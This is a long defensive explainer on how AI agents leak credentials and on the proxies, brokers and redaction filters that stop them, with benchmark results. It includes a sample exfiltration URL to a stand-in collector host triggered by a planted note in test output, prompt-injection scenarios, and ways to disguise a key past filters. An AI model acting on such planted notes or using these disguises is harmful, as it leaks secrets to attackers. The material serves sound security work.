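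The instruction to compare domains doesn't mention `http`. With this instruction, Sonnet 5 still leaked credentials in 12.5% of phishing cases. That is exactly one-eighth, which suggests that nearly all of its remaining leaks involved unencrypted pages. A URL scope that includes the scheme would have blocked those pages regardless of the model's output. It would also help with weaker models such as Qwen, which leaked in 54.7% of cases with the same instruction.

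Ahmed and colleagues also tested whether an agent could avoid a phishing link and still do what the user needed. In the recovery test, a phishing email arrives about a real task, such as an unpaid bill. The agent can find the official address in the stored account details or the official domain in an earlier email. To succeed, it has to log in at the genuine site without giving anything to the fake one.

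Success rates ranged from 0% to 27.7%. GPT-5-mini did best, but it leaked credentials in 10.4% of cases, and in the remaining 61.9% it neither leaked them nor logged in. It succeeded more than twice as often when the account details contained the full address as when it had to find the domain in an old email.

Opus 4.8 never leaked in this test, but it also never completed the task. In 722 of 768 cases, it flagged the message instead. This counts as a failure in the benchmark, but a user may want an assistant to flag a suspicious email about a bill.

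### Leaks between agents

Splitting the release agent into a reader, a tester and a reporter adds places where a credential can end up. A check on the final reply to the release manager would miss a key that one agent passed to another.

*AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) measures how often private data appears in such messages. It uses 1,000 invented tasks from healthcare, finance, law and corporate work. Each task typically gives the agents 29 private facts, of which they need three. An unneeded fact counts as a leak wherever it appears, even if only another agent in the same system reads it.

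They ran the tasks on five models, once with a single agent and once with a coordinator and a worker, for a total of 4,979 paired runs:

| Where the data appeared | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|
| Final reply, single agent | 43.2% |
| Final reply, two agents | 27.2% |
| Messages between the two agents | 68.8% |
| Memory shared by the two agents | 46.7% |

Messages between agents leaked about two and a half times as often as the pair's final replies, and all five models showed the same pattern. In 41.7% of runs, private data leaked internally but did not appear in the final reply. In a smaller test of tool arguments and logs, with 100 tasks per model, the agents put unnecessary private data into tool arguments in 62% to 86% of tasks, depending on the model. For Claude 3.5 Sonnet, the rate was 74% for tool arguments. It was higher for logs, at 85%, because they recorded the model's reasoning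 as well as its actions.

On another set of tasks, telling the agents to protect privacy reduced leaks in final replies to the user from 48% to 19%, but leaks in internal channels only from 31% to 29%. Messages between agents leaked in 69.3% of runs without an attack and 66.3% of runs with a strong one, so most of the leaks were ordinary oversharing rather than the result of attacks.

These percentages don't carry over directly to credentials. The five models date from 2024, and the private facts were things like diagnoses and salaries. El Yagoubi and colleagues classify 82% of the leaks as paraphrases, such as a mention of diabetes in place of a diagnostic code. That paraphrase still reveals the illness, but an API key is useless unless it is reproduced exactly. However, agents that pass their whole context to one another will copy any key it contains verbatim.

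### Counts of credentials in published code

Most counts of leaked credentials come from companies that sell tools for finding them. GitGuardian found 28.65 million new credentials in public GitHub commits (saved sets of changes to a project) in 2025, 34% more than in 2024. Most of these commits had no recorded link to an AI agent, but GitGuardian separately examined those that listed Claude Code as a co-author.

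The reported leak rate for the year was 3.2% for Claude Code's commits and 1.5% for all public commits. Claude Code's monthly rate peaked in August at 31 credentials per 1,000 commits, about 2.4 times the rate for people working alone. By December it had fallen to 13, about the same as the rate for people working alone. The yearly and monthly figures can't have been calculated the same way, because the yearly average is higher than the highest monthly rate, 3.1%. The decline during the autumn is probably more reliable than the exact rates.

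GitGuardian notes that the drop coincided with the release of Claude Sonnet 4.5 in late September. The users also changed as Claude Code's monthly commits rose from 22 in January to 2.16 million in December. For much of the year, its commits had about twice as many lines as other commits, which could explain much of the difference in leaks. GitGuardian also points out that a person decides whether to accept and publish each commit.

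Chen and colleagues found a similar pattern in the skills they studied. Of the 107 with credentials written into their code, 77 had commit messages that mentioned an AI assistant. The study doesn't report how many of the other skills had such messages, so these figures can't show that the assistants made the problem worse.

Configuration files are another source. GitGuardian found 24,008 different credentials in public configuration files for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), and 2,117 of them worked. It partly blames popular setup guides that tell users to put an API key directly in the file. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source MCP servers in which 53% relied on fixed API keys or personal access tokens, while 8.5% used OAuth.

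The harness can also save a credential without involving the model. When a user approves a command in Claude Code and chooses "don't ask again", Claude Code writes the command to a settings file. If the command contains a password, the password is saved too, and the user may publish the file with the rest of the project. Smith (2026), in *The Convenience Click That Put 2,539 Secrets on Public GitHub*, reports that the security company Apiiro traced 2,539 different credentials in 1,994 repositories to these saved approvals. They included database passwords and API keys.

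Some credentials leak through images. Developers often ask a coding agent to attach screenshots to its work so that colleagues can see what changed. *PixelLeak*, by the security company Glow, reports that agents published more than 13,000 internal images on GitHub for developers at over 300 organizations. Some of the images showed credentials, which a scanner that reads only text would miss.

### Credentials memorized in training

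A model can also write a credential that was never in its context if it memorized the string during training. Kenney and colleagues cite several earlier studies in which models reproduced secrets from their training data. The tracker key is different because it reaches the release agent while the agent is working.

Training data contains many live credentials. Truffle Security's *GitHub Repos Exposed 543,699 Credentials. Nobody Revoked Them* (2026) examined The Stack v3, a language-model training set of code from 224 million public repositories. In July 2026, Truffle Security tested the credentials it had found there, and 543,699 still worked. Half of them had been public for more than two years.

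This doesn't show that any particular model can recite the credentials. Models memorize text more readily when it appears many times, and the credentials in this collection appeared about twice each on average. A thief would also find it easier to search the public code directly, as Truffle Security did. Memorization is therefore a smaller danger to the release agent than its own context. If the company created the tracker key after the model was trained, the model can't have memorized it.

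If a key in code written by an agent also appears earlier in the transcript, the agent copied it from its context, and the company should revoke the key and find out how it got into the context. If it doesn't, the model may have memorized someone else's key or made one up, and the company has no key of its own to revoke.

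## Keeping credentials out of the model's reach

A model can't repeat a credential that never enters its context, but developers sometimes put one there on purpose. In Auth0's *Want AI Agents That Don't Spill Secrets?*, Andrea Chiarelli recalls finding an API key in an agent's instructions. This can happen when a tool takes the key as an argument, because the model then needs the key to call the tool. Auth0 recommends removing that argument and having the tool's code look up the key after the model has decided what to do.

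`post_issue` already works this way, but the release agent's key still leaked because the tests inherit the environment variable that holds it. Auth0 recommends environment variables as long as nothing copies their values into the context, but if an agent runs contributors' code, that code could copy them there.

### Swapping a placeholder for the key

The variable can instead contain a placeholder, a harmless string that a trusted component later replaces with the key. That component is usually an egress proxy that the agent's code can't inspect. *From model to agent* (Xu, Zhang and Arunachalam, 2026) explains that OpenAI's hosted containers use this design, so both the model and the container see only placeholders. Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* and Deno's *Security* describe the same design for their own sandboxes.

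Suppose the release agent's tools run in such a sandbox, and the tracker still uses a permanent key. This is how `post_issue` files a report:

1. The company gives the proxy the real key, the variable name `TRACKER_KEY`, and the one host that may receive the key, `api.tracker.example`.
2. The sandbox starts with `TRACKER_KEY` set to `placeholder_7f3a`.
3. The model calls `post_issue` with a title and a description. The tool's code reads the variable and writes the header `Authorization: Bearer placeholder_7f3a`.
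4. The proxy decrypts the request, finds the placeholder and checks that the request is going to `api.tracker.example`.
5. The proxy puts `trk_live_...` in place of the placeholder, encrypts the request again and sends it to the tracker.

Suppose a failing test prints its environment variables and the model follows the planted note. The model can only write `https://collector.example/check?key=placeholder_7f3a`. Even if `read_docs` has no URL scope, the proxy won't insert the key, because `collector.example` isn't the key's host. The contributor gets at most a random string, which won't work if they send it to the tracker from another computer, because the tracker never issued it and the request doesn't pass through the company's proxy.

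A program that bypasses the proxy still sends only the placeholder, so the key is safer than other data in the sandbox, which programs can still send out if the network rules allow it. Deno's sandboxes, for example, can contact any host by default, but Deno sends each credential only to the hosts listed for it.

### Finding the placeholder in a request

The proxy has to decrypt `https` requests to find the placeholder, so the sandbox needs the proxy's certificate. According to 21st.dev's *Security & limits*, the company installs the certificate when it builds the sandbox's template. OpenClaw creates a temporary certificate and uses environment variables to tell common programs where to find it.

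The proxy also needs to know where in the request to look:

| System | Header | Query | Path | Body |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's vaults | Yes | No | No | No |
| Anthropic's vaults | Yes | No | No | Yes |
| OpenShell | Yes | Yes | Yes | If the developer turns it on |
| Gondolin | Yes | If the developer turns it on | No | No |

A simple text search can't find the placeholder in a Basic authentication header, because the program joins the username and password and encodes them in base64. OpenShell and Gondolin, a system that runs code in a virtual machine, decode the header, replace the placeholder and encode the result again.

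A proxy that searches more parts of a request for placeholders works with more programs, but it can also leak the key. Suppose the release agent copies a failed test's output into an issue, and the output includes `placeholder_7f3a`. The request goes to the tracker, which is the right host, but if the proxy replaces placeholders in the body, it will write the real key into an issue that anyone can read. An attacker could cause this deliberately, but it could also happen by accident in an ordinary bug report.

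Anthropic warns that agents often build request bodies from the material they are working on, and describes substituting credentials only in headers as the narrower setting. By default, though, substitution applies to both headers and bodies. fnox, a secrets manager, replaces a placeholder in only one chosen place and rejects any request where the placeholder appears elsewhere or more than once.

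Proxies also differ in how they handle disallowed requests. Anthropic's proxy forwards the literal placeholder if the host or location isn't allowed. According to NVIDIA's *Providers*, OpenShell rejects such a request with an error and records a security finding, without recording the key or the placeholder. It also rejects unknown or expired placeholders. OpenShell's approach is better for the release agent, because the company would learn from the record that something had tried to send its tracker key to `collector.example`.

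Gondolin's *Secrets Handling* warns that a developer's custom code may run after the real key has been substituted into a request, so logging the request's headers from that code could save the key in the proxy's logs.

### Tying a key to its destination

OpenAI's shell tool takes the credentials in a field called `domain_secrets`, next to the list of permitted domains. For the tracker, the developer would write:

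```json
"network_policy": {
  "type": "allowlist",
  "allowed_domains": ["api.tracker.example"],
  "domain_secrets": [{
    "domain": "api.tracker.example",
    "name": "TRACKER_KEY",
    "value": "trk_live_..."
  }]
}
```

The first list determines which hosts the sandbox may contact, and `domain_secrets` determines which of them may receive the key. If the company later added `docs.example.com` to the permitted domains, the key still couldn't go there.

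OpenShell makes two similar but more detailed checks. Its network policy must allow the program to send the request, and the credential's own rule must cover the host, port and path. NVIDIA gives the example of a GitHub credential in a sandbox that may also contact `uploads.example.com`. A request to that host that contains the credential's placeholder gets an error, even though the network policy permits the destination.

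The check on the program is useful for the release agent because `run_tests` and `post_issue` receive the same placeholder. If the policy lets only the `post_issue` program contact the tracker, it blocks a test that tries to send the placeholder there. A list of hosts alone, as in OpenAI's and Anthropic's vaults, can't distinguish the two programs.

A placeholder gives much less protection if the trusted component will replace it for any destination. The first version of mcp-pvp, a project that hides personal data such as email addresses from agents, had this flaw. Its *Capability Security Design* explains that each placeholder came with a signed capability whose destination was "local", which the checking code accepted for every tool. A user might expect the agent to pass a hidden address to `send_email`, but a planted instruction could make the agent pass the same placeholder and capability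 to a tool that sent data to an attacker. The capability was unaltered, so its signature was still valid and mcp-pvp's vault would fill in the real address.

Version 1.0 creates a capability only when the agent plans a call. The capability names the tool and the argument, and lasts five minutes by default. A capability for the `to` argument of `send_email` won't work for `bcc`. This stops an attacker from reusing a capability with another tool or argument, but a misled model can still plan a harmful call and request a capability for it. The vault's policy then has to refuse the request.

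Current products still offer settings with a similar weakness. Anthropic's *Credentials* describes an "unrestricted" option that inserts a key for any host the sandbox may contact, leaving the network policy as the only limit. Daytona, another sandbox provider, says its protection against sending a secret to the wrong host works only if the secret has a list of hosts.

### When the reply contains the key

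The proxy puts the real key in the request, and a permitted server can send it back. This could happen in an example from OpenAI's documentation. The developer allows `httpbin.org` and sets `debug-secret-123` as the key for that domain. The prompt asks the model to call `https://httpbin.org/headers` with the key in a header and report what comes back. That page returns the headers of any request it receives, so the real key will enter the model's context unless something removes it from the reply.

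OpenAI states that raw values don't appear in the context, but doesn't say that the proxy removes credentials from replies. In a later copy of the guide, the Java version of the example calls a page that returns only a status code. It also discards the response body and tells the model never to print headers or secrets. These precautions suggest, but don't prove, that a key echoed in a reply could reach the model. Several of the other versions still use the page that returns headers.

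Other companies are clearer:

| System | What happens to replies |
|---|---|
| Anthropic's vaults | Substitution applies only to outgoing requests |
| OpenShell | The proxy doesn't rewrite the contents of replies |
| Gondolin | The host doesn't substitute anything in replies |
| fnox | The proxy removes a key sent in the query, in plain or percent-encoded form |
| dvergr | The system removes the real value from the reply |

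So replies often arrive unredacted. dvergr, a library for building agents, removes exact copies of the key, which would handle the `httpbin.org` page but could miss a key that the server had encoded differently.

An attacker needs a page that echoes the key on a host where the proxy will insert it. Most ordinary tracker pages wouldn't return the `Authorization` header, but a forgotten debugging page might. OpenShell can exclude such a page by limiting the key to certain paths, but the lists from OpenAI and Anthropic can't because they only specify hosts.

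A service can also reply with a new credential, as in one kind of OAuth login where a program sends a permanent secret and receives an access token. The proxy hides the secret, but the access token arrives in the sandbox as ordinary text. Anthropic advises developers to make this exchange themselves and store the token in the vault. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a proxy that masks OAuth tokens unless the developer sets `passthrough: true`, which sends the real tokens into the sandbox.

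### Signed requests and brokers

Substitution works only if the program sends the key unchanged. Amazon's cloud services use a method called SigV4, in which the program computes a signature for each request with its secret key and sends the signature instead of the key. Amazon also computes the signature and compares the two. A program in the sandbox would sign with the placeholder, so its signature wouldn't match Amazon's. The proxy can't fix this by replacing text, because the placeholder isn't in the request.

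OpenShell solves the problem for SigV4 by having the proxy re-sign the request with the real key, but each signing method needs its own code. DPoP has the same problem, since something outside the sandbox would have to hold the private key and sign the proof. OpenShell also can't insert credentials into connections that don't use HTTP, which rules out many databases.

A program that sends its key unchanged may first check the key's format, so fnox lets the developer choose a placeholder that looks valid, such as one that starts with `ghp_` for GitHub.

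When local code needs the secret for a calculation such as signing, OpenAI advises developers to keep it in their own application and offer the agent a function that does the whole job. Such an application is a broker. The model supplies the details, and the broker builds the request, adds the credential, sends it and decides which parts of the reply to return. (In OpenAI's *Sandbox security*, "credential broker" also covers a proxy that only adds a secret to a request.)

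If `post_issue` were a broker on a separate machine, the sandbox would send it a title and a description. The broker would fill in the tracker's address and the `release` project, and return only the new issue's number. The tests would have no key to inherit, and if a response echoed the key, the broker would not pass it on.

| | Placeholder and proxy | Broker |
|---|---|---|
| Existing command-line programs | Work if they send the key unchanged | Need a new function for each operation |
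| Signed requests | Work if the proxy supports the method | Work |
| Code that builds the request | Runs in the sandbox | Runs outside it |
| Reply that reaches the sandbox | Usually the whole reply | Only the parts that the broker returns |

A broker is the better choice for an agent that performs one operation on one service. Writing a broker for every operation is impractical for a coding agent that runs dozens of command-line programs, but a proxy can protect most of the keys with little extra code.

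Either way, the sandbox may need some credential to identify itself. OpenAI uses a key that the agent's code can read, but that key only lets an environment connect. OpenClaw gives each run a random password for its proxy. An attacker who steals one of these gets far less access than the tracker key would give.

### Using a key without seeing it

An agent can misuse a key it has never seen. If a planted note tells the release agent to fill the tracker with false reports, the proxy will insert the real key into each request because the requests go to the right host. dvergr's documentation calls this remaining risk "use-not-read". A contributor's test can do the same without involving the model if the network rules let it contact the tracker.

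Hiding the key also doesn't protect other data, such as a customer list that the agent copies into an issue, so the company still needs a key with few permissions and a URL scope that specifies methods and paths. It also needs a quick way to withdraw the key. Anthropic applies credential changes and deletions to running sessions without a restart. In OpenAI's Agents API, a sandbox keeps the credential it started with, and deleting the stored copy neither stops the session nor revokes the key at the service. If the release agent were running in such a sandbox and began posting false reports, the company would have to end the session or revoke the key at the tracker.

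### Reference IDs for private data

A placeholder protects only the credentials that the company has registered, so it can't hide a password in a file that the agent opens or a key in an old issue. *SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) extends the idea to private data that arrives in tool results.

SecureClaw puts a trusted gateway between the agent and its tools. When a tool returns private data, the gateway stores it and gives the agent a reference ID, an unpredictable string that stands for the data. The stored record for each ID specifies who may use it, in which session, until when, and where the data may go. The agent also gets a short summary, because it often needs to know something about the data to plan its next step. The summary follows fixed rules that keep at most eight fields or items at each level, cut text off after 512 characters, and hide details such as email addresses and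 account numbers.

Suppose the gateway stores a test log as `LOG_7`, and the agent wants to attach the log to an issue:

1. The agent proposes a call to `post_issue` with the project `release` and the attachment `LOG_7`.
2. The gateway adds the user and session, writes the request in a standard form and computes a keyed hash of it.
3. A policy engine, which is ordinary software with configured rules, approves or refuses that exact request.
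4. A separate program, the executor, computes the hash again and checks that the approval is recent and unused.
5. The executor replaces `LOG_7` with the real log and sends the request.

If the agent changes the project to `payroll` after step 3, the hash changes and the executor rejects the request. In a test, SecureClaw rejected all 25 attacks, which included fabricated requests and reused approvals, and accepted all four legitimate requests.

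Ma and Schmid also compared SecureClaw with an undefended agent on AgentDojo, AgentLeak and Agent Security Bench, another test of attacks on agents that use tools. Both agents used GPT-4o mini, a small model from 2024.

| Test | No defence | SecureClaw |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: attacks that succeeded | 31.5% | 0.6% |
| AgentDojo: tasks completed when there was no attack | 70.1% | 60.8% |
| Agent Security Bench: attacks that succeeded | 91.7% | 0% |
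| Agent Security Bench: tasks completed under attack | 0.9% | 88.9% |
| AgentLeak: attacked runs that leaked private data | 94.0% | 3.2% |

The AgentLeak figure covers final replies, messages between agents and shared memory, but not tool arguments or logs.

Another system in the comparison, Faramesh, checks actions but lets the agent read private data. It stopped every attack on Agent Security Bench, yet leaked in 94.0% of the AgentLeak runs, the same rate as with no defence. Ma and Schmid also removed parts of SecureClaw in a small test with 24 attacked runs for each version. Data leaked between agents in five runs when they removed the reference IDs, but in none when they kept the reference IDs and removed the executor's checks. An agent with private data therefore needs both action checks and data hiding, because they solve separate problems.

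SecureClaw's 88.9% task completion rate is harder to interpret. Faramesh blocked just as many attacks on that benchmark but completed only 3.7% of tasks. When SecureClaw refuses a request, it suggests a safe alternative, such as saving a draft. In a sample of 50 tasks, these suggestions raised completion from 70% to 86%, which leaves most of the difference from Faramesh unexplained. Results were similar on five other model versions, which completed 84% to 94% of tasks with no successful attacks.

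SecureClaw depends on recognizing which data is private, and leaks rose when Ma and Schmid made it miss some fields. A key in a short issue could also remain in the summary if no rule identified it as a key.

All four successful AgentDojo attacks used actions that the policy allowed. In three, the attacker chose the person or account affected. The release agent could fail in a similar way. If `LOG_7` contains a database password and the policy permits attaching logs to issues in `release`, the executor will publish the password, even though the model never saw it.

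## Finding and removing credentials in text

Redaction can remove credentials that have no placeholder, such as a key that an engineer pasted into an issue. A program finds the credential in the text and replaces it, usually with a label such as `[REDACTED]`, before passing the text on.

### Where to put the filter

The harness can filter text at four points:

| Text to filter | What this prevents | What it misses |
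|---|---|---|
| Tool results, before the model reads them | The model repeating a credential from a file or test output | Keys that a user pastes into the chat, or that a tool's own code sends out |
| Tool arguments, before the tool runs | A key in a new issue or a web address | Keys in replies |
| Replies, before anyone reads them | A key in a shared conversation | Keys in tool calls and logs |
| Logs and transcripts, before storage | Someone finding the key later | Anything that has already left |

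Filtering tool results is most effective, because a credential removed there can't reach any later point. SecuritySenses' *Secrets in the Machine*, a webinar summary, also recommends this and points out that an assistant whose replies are filtered can still leak a key by creating a GitHub issue.

Grafana's *PII and secrets redaction* describes two filters for a service that monitors agents. The first removes credentials from the records an application sends to Grafana, but the model has already read the credentials by then. By default, this filter leaves users' messages alone, since people may paste something in on purpose. The documentation contradicts itself on whether the filter scans the model's replies, so developers should test it. The second filter edits requests before they reach the model, but it has to skip the model's earlier reasoning because changing it would invalidate the model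 provider's signature.

An AI agent's reasoning can contain credentials. *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs* (2026) examined 6,708 public agent transcripts that still included the reasoning. The reasoning from real users' sessions contained 62 different API keys. It also contained personal data, and 64 of the 704 private items found there appeared nowhere in the visible conversation.

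### Known formats

Many services give their keys a recognizable shape. A filter can search for these with a regular expression, which is a pattern that describes a set of strings. If a tracker key has 32 random characters after `trk_live_`, the pattern might be:

```text
\btrk_live_[A-Za-z0-9_-]{32}\b
```

Each `\b` requires a boundary between a "word" character (a letter, digit or underscore) and something else, so that the pattern doesn't match part of a longer string. Neither a hyphen nor a quotation mark is a word character, so the pattern fails when the key ends in a hyphen and a quotation mark follows. If all 64 possible characters are equally likely, one key in 64 ends in a hyphen.

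Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, found this mistake in a scanner Mishra had written. The scanner's rules found at least 99.7% of sample keys in each of ten ordinary settings, such as a quoted value or a web address. Five kinds of key can end in a hyphen, and the rate fell to 52% for keys that did. The scanner would silently miss one SendGrid key in 64. Changing the final `\b` to `(?![A-Za-z0-9_])`, which requires only that no word character follows, repaired all five rules.

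Gitleaks, a widely used scanner, had a different flaw. It accepted only certain characters after a key, so it missed some credentials of six of the nine types it could detect. Programmers often test a rule on one or two sample keys in quotation marks, which would reveal neither flaw.

Passwords have no standard format, so scanners look for clues such as `PASSWORD=` in front of them. *SlotGuard* (Xia and Park, 2026) gives an example from an agent's log of how easily this can fail. A command that listed running programs printed `AZURE_OPENAI_KEY="${AZURE_OPENAI_KEY:-...}"`, with the real key in place of the dots. A scanner that expects the key right after the equals sign would miss it.

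### Exact search

If the company holds a credential, its filter can search for that exact string. This needs no pattern and almost never causes a false alarm with a long random key. However, it can't find credentials the company doesn't hold, and it gives attackers another copy of the key to steal.

A filter can store hashes instead. *PRISM* (Tapwal, Kumar and Maple, 2026) describes a system that divides each registered credential into overlapping eight-character pieces and stores the SHA-256 hash of each piece. The system divides and hashes an agent's output in the same way and compares the hashes, so it can also find fragments of a key.

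Plain hashes of such short pieces don't protect a key well. Anyone who steals the list knows that one piece of a tracker key is `k_live_` plus one unknown character, and can find that character in at most 64 guesses. The next piece then has only one unknown character, so recovering all 32 characters takes at most 2,048 guesses. A keyed hash would prevent this if the company stored the hash's secret key somewhere else.

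### Why randomness misleads

Some scanners look for any string that seems random. They usually measure its entropy in bits per character:

```text
H = −Σ p log₂ p
```

Here *p* is each distinct character's share of the string. In `aaaabbcd`, the shares are 1/2, 1/4, 1/8 and 1/8, so H is 0.5 + 0.5 + 0.375 + 0.375 = 1.75 bits. For generic credentials, Gitleaks uses a cutoff of 3.5 bits.

Many keys are hexadecimal, using only the digits 0 to 9 and the letters a to f. With 16 possible characters, the entropy H can't exceed log₂ 16, or 4 bits. The filter that Lan and colleagues tested required more than 4 bits, so no hexadecimal key could trigger it.

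A cutoff of 3.5 catches most long hexadecimal keys, but it also catches harmless strings, such as the hashes that identify commits in Git, the usual system for storing versions of code. A commit hash is typically 40 hexadecimal digits long and usually measures about 3.7 bits. A random 40-digit key usually measures the same, so no cutoff can separate the two.

Short passwords have the opposite problem. A string of *n* characters can't exceed log₂ *n* bits, so no password of 11 characters or fewer can reach 3.5 bits, however random it is. The formula also ignores the order of the characters, so `0123456789abcdef` gets 4 bits, the maximum for 16 characters.

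*Rare Not Random*, a post by the maintainer of a scanner called Betterleaks, suggests measuring how unusual a string is rather than how random it is. The method uses a language model's tokenizer, the software that splits text into tokens. Common words become one or two tokens, while a sample 24-character GitHub key becomes 22. The string's "token efficiency" is its number of characters divided by its number of tokens, and a score below 2.5 suggests a credential.

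The post compares the two measures on CredData, a collection of labelled strings from real code. Precision is the share of alarms caused by real credentials, and recall is the share of real credentials that cause an alarm.

| Test | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Entropy of at least 3.5 bits | 21.1% | 70.4% |
| Token efficiency below 2.5 | 57.3% | 98.6% |
| Token efficiency, ignoring strings with several ordinary words | 80.4% | 95.8% |

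These figures are for classifying strings that the dataset had already picked out, which is easier than finding them in a page of text. The new measure is clearly better, but it fails on passwords made of ordinary words, such as `password123`. It also can't distinguish a commit hash from a hexadecimal key, since both break into short tokens.

### Trained classifiers

The words around a string often help show whether it is a credential when its characters alone don't. For example, "fixed in commit" suggests a hash, while "log in with" suggests a password. A classifier learns to use such clues from labelled examples.

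*IssueGuard* (Rahman, Ahmed and colleagues, 2026) describes a browser extension that warns people before they post a credential in a GitHub issue. The extension finds candidates with 761 regular expressions, then passes each one, with 200 characters of context, to a small language model. When 50 participants checked by eye, 66% still posted a credential, even though the researchers had told them to look for credentials.

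Rahman, Wahab and colleagues (2025), in *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models*, trained Llama-3.1-8B, a small open model, to tell whether candidate credentials in code were real. Across 3,000 candidates, it wrongly flagged 4 and missed 37 real credentials. But half of the candidates were real, a far higher share than in ordinary text.

OpenAI's Privacy Filter, which can run on a laptop, marks credentials and seven kinds of personal data. *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (de Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, 2026) reports a test, on invented text, of how much the filter depends on clues. The filter found 70.8% of credentials when a clue came just before them, 41.6% when it came just after, and 36.1% when there was no clue. The filter can also remove harmless hashes and sample keys by mistake.

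PRISM checks for signs of copying while a model writes. A random key is hard to predict, but once a model starts copying one from its context, it assigns a very high probability to each next character. PRISM combines this signal with 15 others, including whether the text looks like a credential, then lets the text through, masks part of it or stops the model. The full version needs the model's internal probabilities, which a company that rents a model may not be able to get.

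Tapwal and colleagues tested PRISM on 2,000 invented tasks for a team of four agents. A credential leaked in 71.2% of the tasks with no filter and in none with PRISM. Yet they report that PRISM's recall was only 71.2%, compared with 56.2% for a trained classifier, 27.9% for the scanner detect-secrets and 7.0% for another scanner, TruffleHog.

These recall figures are probably too low. For each of these filters, recall and the share of tasks that still leaked add up to exactly 71.2%, which suggests that the calculation included tasks with nothing to find. Among the tasks that leaked without a filter, PRISM prevented the leak in all of them, the classifier in 79%, detect-secrets in 39% and TruffleHog in 10%. No filter caused a false alarm, but results on real text are so different that this test is weak evidence about precision.

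### The same scanner on different text

| Detector | Test data | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| TruffleHog | Candidates from GitHub issues | 55.4% | 93.9% |
| Gitleaks | Candidates from GitHub issues | 49.1% | 90.2% |
| IssueGuard | Candidates from GitHub issues | 92.5% | 92.9% |
| IssueGuard | 178 popular GitHub projects | 51.0% | 86.7% |
| TruffleHog | Live web applications | 89.9% | 36.6% |
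| SecretSifter | Live web applications | 86.3% | 77.8% |
| Betterleaks | CredData | 91.3% | 87.3% |
| Privacy Filter | CredData, counted by token | 74.7% | 96.5% |
| Trained Llama-3.1-8B | Candidates from code, half of them real | 99.7% | 97.5% |

The figures for live web applications come from *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026). TruffleHog found 94% of the credentials in one test and 37% in another, and it stopped about 10% of the leaks in text written by agents. The first test favoured pattern-based scanners because the researchers had collected the candidates with regular expressions.

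IssueGuard's precision fell from 92.5% on its own benchmark to 51.0% on other projects, so a company can't assume a published figure will hold for its agent's text. The company should plant fake credentials in a sample of its own test output and issues, and measure how many the filter finds and how much harmless text it removes.

### Why most alarms can be false

Even a fairly accurate detector produces mostly false alarms if credentials are rare. Suppose that 1,000 out of one million messages contain a credential, and that a detector catches 90% of those but also flags 1% of the harmless messages:

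| | Alarm | No alarm | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Message with a credential | 900 | 100 | 1,000 |
| Harmless message | 9,990 | 989,010 | 999,000 |

There are 10,890 alarms, of which 900 are real. That is about 8%, and the detector has still missed 100 credentials.

The trained Llama model caught 97.5% of the real credentials in the test and wrongly flagged 4 of 1,500 harmless candidates, or 0.27%. If it did equally well on a million messages, 1,000 of which contained real credentials, it would raise 975 real alarms and 2,664 false ones, so about 27% of its alarms would be real. Its precision in the test was much higher, at 99.7%, because half of the test data was real credentials.

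Secret scanners can raise many false alarms on real code. *Argus* (2025) found 370 from TruffleHog and 635 from Gitleaks in ten popular projects. TruffleHog can check a candidate credential by trying it at the service that would have issued it. This removes most false alarms, but it takes time, sends the candidate over the network and works only with services that the scanner supports.

The company's filter could also automatically replace any string that exactly matches a registered key or has the tracker's format, and use weaker clues only where credentials are likely. Grafana's filter, for instance, looks for assignments such as `PASSWORD=` in tool arguments and results but not in the model's own text.

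### Encoded keys

Base64 is a common way to write data using only letters, digits and a few symbols. Chen and colleagues show a skill whose developer put a Base64-encoded credential directly in the code, where anyone could decode it. An exact search for the original credential would not have found it.

Base64 turns each group of three bytes into four characters. Each ordinary letter or digit takes up one byte, so the encoded form of a key depends on where the key falls within the groups. There are three possibilities. These are the results for `trk_live_`, leaving out characters at the edges that also depend on the neighbouring text:

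| Bytes before the key | Encoded form of `trk_live_` |
|---|---|
| 0, 3, 6, ... | `dHJrX2xpdmVf` |
| 1, 4, 7, ... | `Rya19saXZlX` |
| 2, 5, 8, ... | `0cmtfbGl2ZV` |

A filter has to search for all three. It can do the same for a complete key, or it can search for these encoded prefixes to find tracker keys it doesn't hold.

A credential can also be encoded in Base64 more than once. According to Help Net Security, the Betterleaks scanner decodes doubly and triply encoded credentials by default. But a model can just as easily spell the key out as "tango, romeo, kilo", translate the digits into French, or write a poem in which the first letters of the lines form the key, and no finite list can cover every way to disguise it.

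Classifiers can recognize some disguised data without an exact rule for each disguise. In tests on several kinds of private data, Privacy Filter had a recall of 63.1% when the text contained unusual spaces and 67.4% when digits were spelled out as words. A filter with that recall would help against accidental leaks, but an attacker can keep trying disguises until one works.

A reply can even reveal a secret that it doesn't contain in any form. In *LLMs Leak Secrets Through Unrelated Outputs*, Bhardwaj, Kaya and colleagues (2026) gave the model Qwen3-8B a four-digit PIN and told it to keep the PIN secret. They then asked it for lists of ten random even numbers and discarded any list that contained the PIN, its digits in another order, or a number that differed from the PIN by one digit.

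The PIN still slightly changed which numbers the model was likely to choose. Bhardwaj and colleagues ran the same model with different candidate PINs and calculated how likely it was to produce the remaining lists with each one. Using about 20 lists per PIN, they picked the correct PIN out of 10,000 possibilities in 24 of 50 cases, and had it among their top five guesses in 36.

This attack requires the model's weights, the format of the secret and a close copy of the prompt. Bhardwaj and colleagues didn't test it on API keys, and searching the 2¹²⁸ possible values of a long random key is much harder than searching 10,000 PINs. But a filter that searches the reply for the secret couldn't have stopped the attack, so the only sure protection is to keep the secret out of the context.

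### A key split between two chunks

Many assistants stream their replies, which means that they send the text in small chunks as the model writes it. Suppose that a short tracker key is `trk_live_Q7x9` and that the reply arrives like this:

```text
Chunk 1: The key is trk_li
Chunk 2: ve_Q7x9 for now.
```

Neither chunk contains the whole key, so a filter that checks each chunk separately lets both through. To prevent this, the filter can hold back the end of the text until more arrives. The key has 13 characters, so the filter must hold back 12:

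1. After the first chunk, the filter sends `The k` and keeps `ey is trk_li`.
2. When the second chunk arrives, it adds the new text to what it kept and gets `ey is trk_live_Q7x9 for now.`
3. It finds the key and replaces it before sending any more.

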